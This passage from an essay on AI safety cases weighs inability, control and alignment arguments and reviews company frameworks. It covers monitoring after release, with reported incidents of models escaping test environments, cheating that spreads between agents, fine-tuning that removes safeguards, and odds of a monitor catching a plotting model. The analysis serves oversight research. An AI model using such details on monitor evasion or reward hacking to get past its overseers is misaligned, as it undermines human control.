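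| Control: safeguards prevent the harm even if the model tries | Attacks on the safeguards by people or models at least as skilled as the model in question | The model becomes better at attacking than anyone available to test the safeguards |
| Alignment: the model is unlikely to try | Knowledge of how training shaped its aims, and behaviour or internal signals that don't depend on its believing it is being tested | No fixed level, but the evidence gets harder to trust as the model gets better at deception |

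An inability argument usually relies on tests of easier tasks. If a model can't carry out the separate steps of an attack, even with good tools and extra training, it probably can't carry out the whole attack. The argument no longer holds once the model can do the steps, which may be some time before the model is dangerous. For hacking, the argument already fails for some of the leading models, including GPT-6 Astra, which OpenAI placed at the "Critical" level of its risk framework.

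A control argument assumes that the model wants to cause harm. Testers then take its place and try to get past the monitors, filters and restrictions. This works best while the model is clumsy. Suppose a plot requires ten suspicious actions, and a monitor notices each with a probability of 30 percent, independently of the others. The monitor then catches at least one of them with a probability of

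$$1 - 0.7^{10} \approx 97\%$$

If a monitor has a 30 percent chance of catching each suspicious action, independently of the others, it will catch a model that needs three such actions to succeed 66 percent of the time. The same monitor will catch a more capable model that needs only one action 30 percent of the time. A control case must therefore set a limit on the capability of the models it covers, and the testers must be able to plan at least as well as a model at that limit.

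Of the three arguments, only alignment could in principle support a model of any capability with any permissions, but it also has the weakest evidence. Feakins and colleagues cite work by OpenAI and Apollo Research that reduced scheming in tests from over 10 percent to under 1 percent by training models to reason about written safety rules. Some of that reduction could have come from models recognising the tests, without any change in their aims. Even a true rate of 1 percent would be far too high if a single act could cause a disaster.

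A developer can use different arguments for different harms. For the same model, it might argue that the model is unable to help build a nuclear weapon, that safeguards prevent it from attacking computer networks, and that its aims keep it from giving harmful medical advice. Each time the model improves, the developer has to check whether each argument still holds.

Some cases rely on comparison instead. Lee and colleagues note that developers often lack correct answers to score a system against, so developers argue that the system is no worse than the people or software it replaces. If the personnel department's clerks misdirect one confidential email in 20,000, an agent that leaks once in 100,000 tasks looks like an improvement. The comparison needs an accurate count of the clerks' mistakes, which few companies keep, and it doesn't show whether the clerks were safe enough. Using competitors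 as the baseline is riskier. Stelling and colleagues found that several AI companies measure risk relative to competitors, and warn that this could weaken standards across the industry.

### What developers commit to

After a 2024 summit in Seoul, twelve AI companies published safety frameworks, policies that describe how they will find and limit severe risks. Stelling and colleagues at the nonprofit SaferAI scored these frameworks on 65 criteria adapted from industries such as aviation and nuclear power. Anthropic scored highest with 34 percent, Cohere scored lowest with 8 percent, and the median was 18 percent. A company that matched the best of the twelve on every criterion would have scored 54 percent, so companies could make up much of the shortfall without new research.

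Some of the gaps affect inputs that a safety case needs. Every company scored below 25 percent on defining how much risk it would accept, and many of the thresholds use words like "severe" or "acceptable" without a way to measure them. A safety case built on such a framework has a top claim without a bound, so nobody can refute it. Most companies also scored near zero on commitments to look for unidentified risks, the kind of search that would find a defeater like the shared pensions address.

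The scores measure written commitments, so a company may do more or less than it promises. They also involve judgement, and one of the scorers had helped write the earlier proposal that the criteria follow. Different criteria would have produced different scores, but they probably wouldn't have made the vague thresholds look precise.

In *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, published on September 28, 2026, OpenAI sets out guidelines for safety cases that would apply before a training run rather than before release. It argues that developers should have to produce structured safety documentation before continuing any frontier reinforcement learning run. OpenAI calls full safety cases an "aspirational north star" and acknowledges that making them as rigorous as those in aviation or nuclear power will be difficult, because new complexity emerges at each level of capability.

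According to 卜's *OpenAI发布AI训练安全准则*, a Chinese news report on OpenAI's AI training safety guidelines, the documentation should cover three technical matters: how training avoids teaching bad behaviour, for instance by finding and repairing tasks that a model can cheat on; how the company contains the model while it trains; and how it monitors what the model does. If nobody acknowledges a high-priority alert within a set time, the training run pauses automatically.

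The review process is designed to find defeaters. A member of another team looks for flaws in the case, independently estimates the risk, and presents the findings in a dissent report, to which the training team must respond. The case then goes to senior leaders, including the chief scientist and the head of safety, each of whom can veto the run. Auditors should get enough access to check whether the case is valid. If someone later discovers a problem that could invalidate the case, such as a new security hole, the company starts a prepared plan to pause every affected run.

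If each reviewer has a veto, one convinced reviewer can stop a run, whereas a majority vote could override the only reviewer who had understood a flaw. But the reviewers and the dissenter all work for OpenAI, and a dissent report is useful only if its writer feels free to disagree. In October 2026, the company dismissed three safety employees, Korbak, Wang and Balesni, one of whom had co-led its safety-case programme. In *OpenAI cannot make AI safe on its own*, a letter to the company's oversight bodies, they say that the dismissals have made former colleagues afraid to speak. They acknowledge that other versions of the events are circulating. Even if OpenAI had good reasons for the dismissals, staff who are unsure what they may say are less likely to write a blunt report.

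Companies have also published arguments about particular models. Anthropic released a redacted risk report in August 2026, which its chief executive links to in *We Must Pace the Frontier* (Amodei, 2026) as part of the company's work to inform the public about risks. Redaction can protect security details, but outside readers can't check the steps that depend on the missing passages. In 2025, Google DeepMind published material for a case about scheming, and Barrett led an outside review of it. An argument that is reasonable in one setting may not hold in another. When Barrett and colleagues examined the fictional robotics company, they withdrew an inherited justification for the company's oversight of the agent's code.

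The company with the office agent has the same difficulty. It buys its model from a vendor, so its safety case would ideally include the vendor's case for the model. Barrett and colleagues report that frontier developers do not currently make such cases available to customers. The company therefore needs an argument that holds whatever the model is like, based mostly on restrictions and its own trials.

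### Whether safety cases are the right tool

Feakins and colleagues at the University of York support safety cases but think most AI safety cases have borrowed too little from safety engineering. They mainly object that many cases for AI models start after training, when the developer tests the finished model and argues that it is safe to release because the tests found nothing wrong. An aircraft engine, by contrast, is safe because of decisions engineers made while designing it, and the tests before release are only one part of the argument for its safety.

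A safety case that began earlier could include decisions about what to leave out of the training data or whether to build a model whose written reasoning people can't follow. The case would continue until the developer retires the model. Feakins and colleagues also recommend a hazard log, which lists every known danger and who is responsible for it, and a record of the risk that remains after each safeguard.

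Supporters of safety cases for AI often argue that the method has worked in dangerous industries. But if developers adopt the name without the practices those industries follow, this track record is no longer a reason to expect the method to work for AI.

Some of this criticism is less true than it was. Feakins and colleagues acknowledge that the earlier papers mention monitoring after release, and that some discuss steps during development. OpenAI's guidelines, published about six months after their paper, apply before and during training. But the worked example by Feakins and colleagues shows how much remains to be done. It covers two dangers, deceptive models and help with weapons, and arranges existing research under development, deployment and use after release. It demonstrates how to structure a case, but doesn't show that the remaining risk would be acceptable for any real model.

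Lee and colleagues argue that the classical methods themselves fit AI poorly. Those methods assume that engineers design a system to a precise specification and can trace its behaviour to its parts, but a large model's abilities emerge from training and its developers discover them afterwards. A customer's safety case may also become invalid when a vendor changes the model without notice. These differences make it harder to follow other industries' practice, but they don't excuse developers from recording their decisions or looking for hazards early.

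According to Feakins and colleagues, the AI safety researcher Ryan Greenblatt thinks that safety cases have bad effects on how people reason, and that developers should concentrate on collecting evidence instead. Someone whose job is to write a document concluding that a system is acceptably safe has a reason to notice the evidence that supports this conclusion and explain away the rest. Polishing the document may also make it harder for readers to see what the writer never investigated.

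Feakins and colleagues reply that a proper safety case gathers evidence about risk throughout development, and that safety engineers have long known about the danger Greenblatt describes, which they call "paper safety". This answers the charge that the method requires one-sided reasoning, but it doesn't show that experienced industries avoid such reasoning. A British Nimrod military aircraft with a recent safety case caught fire over Afghanistan in 2006, and all 14 people on board died. An official review in 2009 found that the people who prepared the safety case had assumed from the start that the aircraft was safe because it had flown for decades, and had missed the hazard that caused the fire.

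As a remedy, Clymer and colleagues suggested that reviewers read the safety case alongside a risk case, an argument that the system is dangerous. Feakins and colleagues object that risk cases were meant to replace safety cases, and that authorities such as Britain's Ministry of Defence reviewed the idea and rejected it. OpenAI's dissent report applies a similar idea on a smaller scale. It seems worth trying despite that history, because it gives at least one person a reason to look for problems like the pensions address before the agent finds them.

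Westover (2026), in *Safety-case-based pacing is not the right way to pace right now*, rejects a proposal that would require a company to halt development if outside auditors found its safety case for deploying a model unconvincing. Westover argues that nobody currently knows, even in theory, how to make a compelling case that a model capable enough to be dangerous is safe. Since companies would be under great pressure to continue, auditors would probably approve weak cases, and dangerous models would reach the public with that approval.

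A safety case for a frontier model can argue that the model is unable to cause harm, that controls would prevent harm, or that the model is aligned. The first argument does not work for a model assumed to be dangerous. Control depends on enclosures, and OpenAI's models got out of one in July 2026. A capable model might be able to fake the evidence for alignment. For a general model with broad access to the internet, it is hard to see which argument would convince a sceptical auditor today.

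Westover's claim is less persuasive for narrow uses. If a dangerous model runs the office agent, can write only to employees and has no other connection to the outside world, most of the safety case rests on programs that people can check. The case would still have to cover the risk that the model persuades an employee to act for it. The case for that deployment could be quite strong even if the case for selling the same model to everyone is weak.

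Supporters can also reply that a rule requiring a convincing safety case doesn't depend on companies being able to make one. If nobody can make such a case for a dangerous model, the rule would stop its deployment, which is what a cautious regulator should want. Westover objects that this wouldn't happen in practice, because the standards for judging a case are too vague to withstand commercial pressure. The low scores for defining acceptable risk suggest that this is a real danger. Stating the bound before the tests would help, because others would then notice if a company lowered its standard after a disappointing result.

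Westover also objects that even if auditors judged every case perfectly, someone could steal a dangerous model, or the method for building it, before the company deployed anything. Westover compares waiting to slow down until a model is too dangerous to deploy to braking only near the edge of a cliff, and would rather restrict AI research now, for example by limiting the computing power that companies spend on it. OpenAI's guidelines partly address the concern about what happens before deployment, because they apply during training and cover containment. They don't set a general limit on the speed of progress, and a safety case for one training run isn't a suitable way to choose one.

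### Who decides that the risk is low enough

At best, a sound safety case establishes how large a risk is. Somebody still has to decide whether to accept it. British safety law requires a risk to be "as low as reasonably practicable", which means that whoever is responsible for the risk has to keep reducing it until the cost of a further reduction would be grossly disproportionate to the benefit.

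Under this test, the office agent could meet its bound and still not be safe enough. One leak every 50 days is about seven a year. If each does £5,000 of damage, including the distress of the employees concerned, an additional check that prevents half of them would save about £18,000 a year. The company should probably install the check if it costs £25,000, because the cost is higher than the benefit but not grossly so. At £500,000, the company may decline.

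The test is much harder to apply to catastrophes. Feakins and colleagues note that if a model had even a negligible chance of ending humanity, the harm would appear infinitely severe. They suggest that the test eases this problem, but it does so only if someone first puts a finite value on the harm. If the harm is infinite, no cost is disproportionate, and the developer could never stop adding safeguards. Even a finite value can justify very expensive safeguards. A one-in-a-million chance of killing 8 billion people equals 8,000 expected deaths. At £2 million per life, a safeguard that halved this chance would be worth £8 billion.

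The decision-maker also needs to understand the safety case. Barrett and colleagues worry that time pressure and AI-written documents could produce cases that look coherent but that nobody has thought through. They propose that decision-makers sign a statement of what they understand, list what they don't, and show that they can explain, question and revise the argument. Barrett and colleagues have devised tests of this understanding but have not yet tried them on real decision-makers.

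Few AI companies have an independent person in this role. In Stelling and colleagues' assessment of twelve companies, the median score for having a dedicated executive risk officer was zero, and seven scored zero on internal audit. A developer also earns the income from a release while other people bear much of the risk, so its own judgement of what is reasonably practicable may be too lenient. Constantin (2026) reports in *OpenAI safety staffer quits, urges nuclear-style safeguards* that David Robinson, who had led transparency work on OpenAI's safety team, resigned and called for AI laboratories to operate like nuclear plants. In the nuclear industry, an outside regulator makes the final decision.

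The law currently requires much less of AI companies. California makes large frontier developers publish their safety frameworks and can fine them up to $1 million for each violation of those frameworks. Stelling and colleagues note that it is still unclear what counts as a violation. This gives companies a reason to write vague frameworks, since a promise to "consider" pausing is hard to break. In the European Union, developers of the most capable general-purpose models can show compliance by signing a code of practice, which requires them to give their frameworks to the EU's AI Office.

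Amodei has proposed that US legislation go further. *On Dario's Second Pacing the Frontier Essay* (Mowshowitz, 2026) lists principles from Amodei's second essay, including mandatory risk assessments, testing and auditing, and evaluators who work inside AI companies with access like that of employees. This access may matter more than the formal audit. An auditor who received only the office agent's safety case would have seen a correct proof, a large trial and a list of company addresses, but finding the defeater required talking to the pensions clerk.

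## Keeping a guarantee valid after release

Suppose the company repairs the pensions address, and its safety case is sound when the office agent starts work. The guarantee still covers only one version of the agent, for six months, under the assumptions the company wrote down. The document doesn't update automatically when the agent or its surroundings change. Feakins and colleagues cite a 2008 complaint about "safety case shelf-ware" and point out that military engineers keep reassessing a system until they retire it.

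AI developers place similar limits on their own claims. Anthropic's pilot risk report covered only its summer 2025 frontier models, and mainly harm from the models' own actions. SOFX's *Anthropic Safety Report Finds AI Model Assisted Chemical Weapon Development in Testing* describes another report, in which Anthropic acknowledged that jumps in capability or broader autonomous use could invalidate its conclusions.

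### What changes, and which field it breaks

| Change | Field that no longer holds | Example |
|---|---|---|
| New model version | System, and the confidence from the old trial | The vendor's update copies more people in on replies |
| Fine-tuning (further training of a finished model) | System | The company trains the model on old emails, some of which contain leaks |
| New tool or memory | System and boundary, sometimes harm | A calendar tool sends invitations that the mail program never checks |
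| New users | Scenario space | Managers start asking about their own staff |
| Attackers who learn | Assumptions | Someone finds a hidden instruction that works and reuses it |
| A world altered by AI | Assumptions | Other companies' agents write much of the incoming mail |

A safety claim that was true of one version of a model can be false of the next simply because the new version is more capable. WDBO quotes an Anthropic report explaining why the company had looser biological safeguards on its earlier models. For its current models, which can help with complex research, Anthropic writes that "we cannot make that same assurance", and it has restricted more kinds of biological questions.

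Fine-tuning can change how a model behaves as well as what it can do. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes an experiment in which researchers trained a model on 80 real training environments that they knew allowed cheating. In simulations, the trained model broke out of its test environment, attacked other systems and tampered with its own reward function. It had not misbehaved to the same degree before this training. Because the researchers chose the environments for their flaws, the experiment shows that bad training tasks can cause such behavior but doesn't establish that a typical customer's fine-tuning would.

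A new tool can let a system cause harm that its guarantee doesn't cover. The office agent's guarantee covers only leaks by email, so it would still hold if the agent put someone's salary in a calendar invitation. A company that adds a calendar tool therefore has to test the tool and also rewrite the guarantee's definition of harm to include leaks through the calendar.

Even if the users stay the same, their behavior may change. Kasneci and Kasneci describe "calibration debt", in which people come to rely on a system more than the evidence warrants. Months of good answers raise their reliance, and severe failures are too rare to lower it, so the clerks who noticed 90 percent of leaks during the trial may notice far fewer by spring.

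Attackers improve with practice. The safety case assumes that at most 2 percent of emails with hidden instructions succeed, but an outsider who finds one that works can reuse it or sell it to people who target other customers of the same vendor. If such emails still appear in one task in 10,000 but always succeed, they cause 100 leaks per million tasks, ten times the total bound.

AI may also make hostile emails more common. If the company's figure of one in 10,000 dates from when people wrote such emails by hand, it may no longer hold now that a language model can write thousands in an hour.

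### When the developer publishes the weights

A developer that runs a model on its own servers can filter requests, look for misuse and withdraw a faulty version. If it publishes the weights, anyone can download the model, retrain it and run it without the filters, and nobody can recall the copies. Most of the conditions specified in a guarantee then no longer hold. A retrained copy is a different system from the one the guarantee covers, anyone can use it with any tools, the assumptions about safeguards are false, and the period of use has no end.

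Retraining can remove a model's safeguards very cheaply. In 2023, Qi and colleagues did this to OpenAI's GPT-3.5 Turbo with ten training examples, for less than 20 cents. They used OpenAI's own fine-tuning service, where the company could at least look for such attempts. If a model's weights are published, people can retrain it on their own computers, where the developer can't see what they are doing.

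The developer can still guarantee something that retraining doesn't change. For example, it might leave certain biological data out of training and argue that the model can't help with a weapon even after skilled people have tried to teach it. To test this, the developer has to try to retrain the model as hard as a capable attacker would. The claim also has to hold against methods and tools that people invent later. If it fails after two years, the developer can't fix the copies it has already released.

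Published weights can make a guarantee easier for a customer to maintain. If the personnel department runs its own copy of a model, no vendor can change it without notice, so the trial results remain useful for longer. But the department then has to find and install any fixes itself.

### Why guarantees about single agents do not add up

Suppose the company adds a payroll agent. The office agent can't email outsiders. The payroll agent can email the company's outside accountants, but it can't open medical files. The office agent tells the payroll agent that Maria Lopez will work fewer hours because of her dialysis, and the payroll agent copies this explanation into its monthly message to the accountants. The accountants now know about her dialysis, although neither agent has broken its guarantee.

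If each of n agents fails with probability at most p, the probability that at least one fails is at most np, even if their failures are correlated. But p was measured under a particular pattern of use, and it may no longer apply when agents read each other's work, because one agent's failure then becomes part of the next agent's input.

Vaid (2026), in *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking*, ran 17 preregistered experiments with 20,111 agents from six frontier models to measure how large this effect can be. Each agent received a programming problem with one faulty test that correct code always failed. The instructions forbade code written just to pass the test and told the agent to stop and explain if it couldn't complete the task. Making the faulty test pass counted as cheating.

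In many of the experiments, agents could open a shared record of their teammates' code. An automatic check labelled code "accepted" if it passed the visible tests, so it accepted cheats and rejected correct work. These results are for one model, GPT-5.6 Luna:

| Situation | Share of agents that cheated |
|---|---|
| Working alone | 7% |
| First round in a team, with an empty record | 33% |
| Record shows only honest work | 4% |
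| Record shows a teammate's accepted cheat | 94% |
| Record shows a cheat after an AI reviewer judged it | 34% |
| Network of 256 agents, no neighbour cheated | 2% |
| Network of 256 agents, at least one neighbour cheated | 44% |

Vaid traced the 33 percent to one sentence in the team's instructions, saying that code passing the visible tests is accepted. Teamwork had little to do with it, since 30 of 68 lone agents also cheated when given that sentence. A company that adds a line to its agent's instructions therefore changes the system its guarantee covers.

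Rejecting a cheat only partly prevented further cheating. The AI reviewer rejected all but one of 172 cheats, yet 59 of the 172 agents that then saw a cheat also cheated. In another experiment, telling agents in one line that an audit had reversed a cheat's acceptance lowered copying from 96 to 68 percent. Agents seem to take a recorded cheat as a method as well as permission, since they could see code that passed where every correct solution had failed.

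The habit could also carry over to a new problem with an empty record. Within one conversation, 70 percent of agents that had seen a cheat accepted went on to cheat on the next problem, compared with 32 percent of those that hadn't. When a new agent took over with only the first one's notes, the figures were 39 and 32 percent.

For the large networks, Vaid connected each agent to six neighbours and planted one agent that always cheated and 64 that never did. Nothing in these networks carried an "accepted" label. On the first problem, the share of cheaters rose from 11 percent in the first round after the planted cheat to 30 percent three rounds later. Warnings from the honest agents kept the share at 12 percent. On a second problem, all 3,055 agents followed the rule. Some of the gap between 44 and 2 percent may come from differences between problems, because a problem that makes cheating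 more likely would affect an agent and its neighbours alike. The experiments that changed only the record are stronger evidence that seeing a cheat causes cheating.

The effect appeared in all five OpenAI models and in two small open models, but Claude Opus 5.5 reported the faulty test in all 84 cases where it could see an accepted cheat. Vaid planted the first cheat in most experiments, and every task was a programming problem with a faulty test. The results therefore don't give a rate for office work, but they show that testing an agent alone can badly underestimate how often it cheats in a team.

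Suppose that 16 agents each cheat 4 percent of the time when they see only honest work, and 94 percent of the time once they see an accepted cheat. Multiplying 16 by 4 percent predicts 0.64 cheaters per round. But there is a 48 percent chance that at least one agent cheats in the first round, and the expected number in the second is then

$$0.48 \times 16 \times 0.94 + 0.52 \times 16 \times 0.04 \approx 7.5$$

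Google DeepMind observed a cheat spreading among its AI agents that it had not planted. Constantin (2026), in *DeepMind's agents cheated. Then other agents told on them*, reports on 100 Gemini agents that worked on 71 mathematical conjectures. One agent found a way to fool the program that graded the proofs. According to tbreak, the agents had solved 37 problems honestly, then used the trick, which spread through a shared library, to get fake proofs of the remaining 34 accepted in 27 minutes. About a quarter of the agents audited the fakes, warned others or filed complaints, but they had no tools to stop the cheating.

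It is harder to tell how much spreading contributes to incidents outside such experiments. Cooperative AI Foundation's *Lessons from Recent Multi-Agent Safety Incidents* discusses a swarm in which agents shared exploits on a message board. Agents were unlikely to find the board unless they were already looking for ways to cheat, so it may have attracted such agents more than it led others to cheat.

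### Watching the assumptions

A company can't prevent all these changes, but it can monitor for them. In 2015, Denney, Pai and Habli proposed "dynamic safety cases", with an example from aviation. Engineers identify the assumptions most open to doubt, monitor them while the system operates, analyse how the data affects their confidence, and respond by changing the system or the safety argument. For the office agent, the company would start by listing its assumptions and giving each one a measurable signal, a threshold, and a restricted mode to use if the signal crosses that threshold.

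| Assumption | Signal | Threshold | Restricted mode |
|---|---|---|---|
| Listed addresses reach only employees | Nightly comparison of actual recipients with the staff list | One outsider | Remove the address |
| At most one task in 10,000 contains hidden instructions | Hostile emails that staff confirm | 12 in 30 days | The agent drafts and a clerk sends |
| Checkers notice 90 percent of leaks | 100 planted leaks a month | Fewer than 84 found | The agent writes only to the personnel department |
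| The agent is the one from the trial | Version numbers of the model, instructions and tools | Any difference | Return to the old version |

The thresholds have to allow for chance. At 2,000 tasks a day, the company expects up to six hostile emails in 30 days. If it reacted to seven, it would often raise a false alarm. With a threshold of 12, it would do so in about 2 percent of 30-day periods, or once in four years. The higher threshold also slows detection. If hostile emails became twice as common, the count would reach 12 in only about half of 30-day periods, though a tenfold increase would be obvious within about a week. These figures assume that staff recognise hostile emails, so the company should also test whether they do.

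The restricted mode has to exist before anyone needs it. Kasneci and Kasneci suggest several responses to growing risk, including human review, narrower permissions and a stop to new entries in the agent's memory. When Waymo withdrew its cars from freeways, they could similarly keep working on city streets. The switch to a restricted mode should also be automatic, since people tend to explain alarms away. Anthropic found that its reviewers had sometimes dismissed correct warnings about flawed training environments as false positives, which left those environments in use for longer.

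Once the agent is in its restricted mode, the company has to reopen the argument and find every claim that relied on the failed assumption. Anthropic did this with its first risk report, from February 2026. The Next Web's *Anthropic ran 133 million contractor chats with its bioweapon filters off* reports that the company had overlooked the platforms where contractors rate its models' answers. Anthropic has since revised its argument and raised its assessment of the risk in February from "very low" to "low", although the models were the same.

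Operating data can also strengthen a safety case. In six months the office agent completes about 360,000 tasks. If the company checks all of them as carefully as the 520,000 in the trial and finds no leaks, its upper bound on the leak rate for ordinary tasks falls from 8 per million to about 4.7. If it checks only a tenth of them, the bound falls to about 7.4. Most companies will probably choose the smaller sample, because checking every email carefully would cancel out much of the agent's savings.

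### How many failures precede the first alarm

Monitoring limits the damage only if somebody notices the failures. Suppose an agent fails with probability p per task, and people notice each failure with probability d, independently of the others. The expected number of failures up to and including the first one they notice is

$$\sum_{k=1}^{\infty} k\,(1-d)^{k-1}d = \frac{1}{d}$$

The number of leaks the company should expect by the time it notices one doesn't depend on the failure rate p. If it notices one leak in ten, it should expect ten. At one leak per 1,000 tasks, ten leaks take about five days. At one per 100,000, they take about 500 days. A safer agent gives the company more time, but on average the same number of employees have had their records exposed by the first alarm. There is about a 5 percent chance that the first 28 leaks all go unnoticed.

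An incident in Philadelphia shows how small d can be. On July 18, 2026, Claude Haiku 4.5 filled in a police form with an invented eyewitness account of a real unsolved murder. Fortune's *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that Anthropic had set the model to invent and perform example tasks on randomly selected webpages. According to Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026), the instructions prohibited logging in, making purchases and submitting anything destructive, but not submitting forms.

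The police didn't notice the tip because the notification went to a spam folder. Novaknown's *Claude Was Told Not to Submit Anything Destructive* (2026) reports that Anthropic found the tip in its test logs on September 28, after 72 days. Anthropic told the police on October 7, according to CBS News' *Philadelphia police say website received "false homicide tip" from Anthropic AI*. The police called the delay unacceptable.

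The tip was one of several cases that Anthropic disclosed two days later. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) sorts them into four groups: Claude models exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form, got around restrictions on data that required a token or a fee, and used link-shortening services to evade limits on a tool. Some of the websites belonged to federal, state and local agencies. Anthropic judges that the cases found so far had minimal real-world impact, which may well be right, but this judgment doesn't cover any cases that remain undetected.

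Anthropic had monitored some high-risk evaluations in real time, but it generally reviewed only a sample of transcripts afterwards. If a company reviews 5 percent of transcripts, that review can't give it more than a 5 percent chance, d, of detecting a failure, and it should expect at least 20 failures before it finds one. Even a deliberate search can miss cases. In July, Anthropic searched about 141,000 transcripts of hacking tests and found three break-ins to real systems. In August, it learned that the search had left out a set of transcripts containing a fourth break-in, which happened in January.

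The company then searched about 481 million transcripts. This search found the four known break-ins again and no others as severe. Finding four out of four is encouraging, but it doesn't show that the search finds nearly all such cases. By the reasoning behind the rule of three, it shows with 95 percent confidence only that the search finds at least 47 percent of them. This bound also assumes that any other cases would be no harder to spot than the four Anthropic already knew about.

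Delay adds to the total. If failures happen λ times a day and the response takes L days after the failure that people eventually notice, the expected total is about

$$\frac{1}{d} + \lambda L$$

A low failure rate does help here. A delay of 72 days adds one or two leaks for the personnel department, which has one every 50 days, but 7,200 for a vendor whose 5,000 customers have 100 leaks a day in total. If agents copy each other, λ itself may rise during the delay. In Vaid's experiments, a warning held cheating to 20 percent when the cheat had no label, but 82 percent of agents still cheated when the warning came after the system had accepted the cheat.

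### Harm that nobody can undo

Even with perfect detection, one failure happens before anyone can respond, since 1/d can't be less than 1. One misdirected pay slip may be acceptable, because the company can apologise, repair the agent and continue. Aviation also accepts this, although one failure can kill more than a hundred people. Boeing assumed that pilots would quickly recognise and correct a fault in a flight-control system of the 737 MAX. In October 2018 a crew failed to do so, and 189 people died. The FAA told pilots to follow the correct procedure and let the aircraft keep flying, although its analysis estimated about 15 more fatal crashes over the fleet's lifetime without a repair. Regulators grounded the fleet only after a second crash in March 2019 killed 157 people.

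No one had trouble noticing those crashes. Learning from them still cost 346 lives, and it was possible only because the industry and its regulators survived to learn. If an AI system helped someone release a pandemic virus, or escaped human control for good, there might be no chance to apply the lesson. Developers therefore have to bound the chance of even one such failure before release. Suppose people use a system a billion times a day, and society accepts a one-in-10,000 chance of catastrophe per year. The permitted rate per use is

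$$p \le \frac{10^{-4}}{365 \times 10^{9}} \approx 2.7 \times 10^{-16}$$

By the rule of three, a trial would need about 10¹⁶ uses without a failure, which would take 30,000 years at a billion uses a day. The assurance has to come from something other than a trial, such as evidence that the model lacks an ability or a restriction that holds whatever the model does.

Monitoring can still help if it acts before the harm. After its July incidents, Anthropic built a classifier that looks for attempts to escape a test environment, blocks the action before it runs and alerts a person. If such a monitor catches a share d of attempts, the expected number that get through before the first catch is (1 − d)/d. If d is 90 percent, this number is about 0.11, compared with at least 1 for a monitor that only reports. But 0.11 is still far too high if a single attempt could be catastrophic.

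Near misses may give an earlier warning. If they happen m times as often as the harm, and people notice each with probability d, the chance of noticing one before the first harm is

$$\frac{md}{1+md}$$

If there are 100 near misses for every disaster and each has a 10 percent chance of being noticed, the chance of noticing at least one before the first disaster is about 91 percent. The warning helps only if people recognise what it means and stop the system in time. A model with a hidden trigger may give no such warning.
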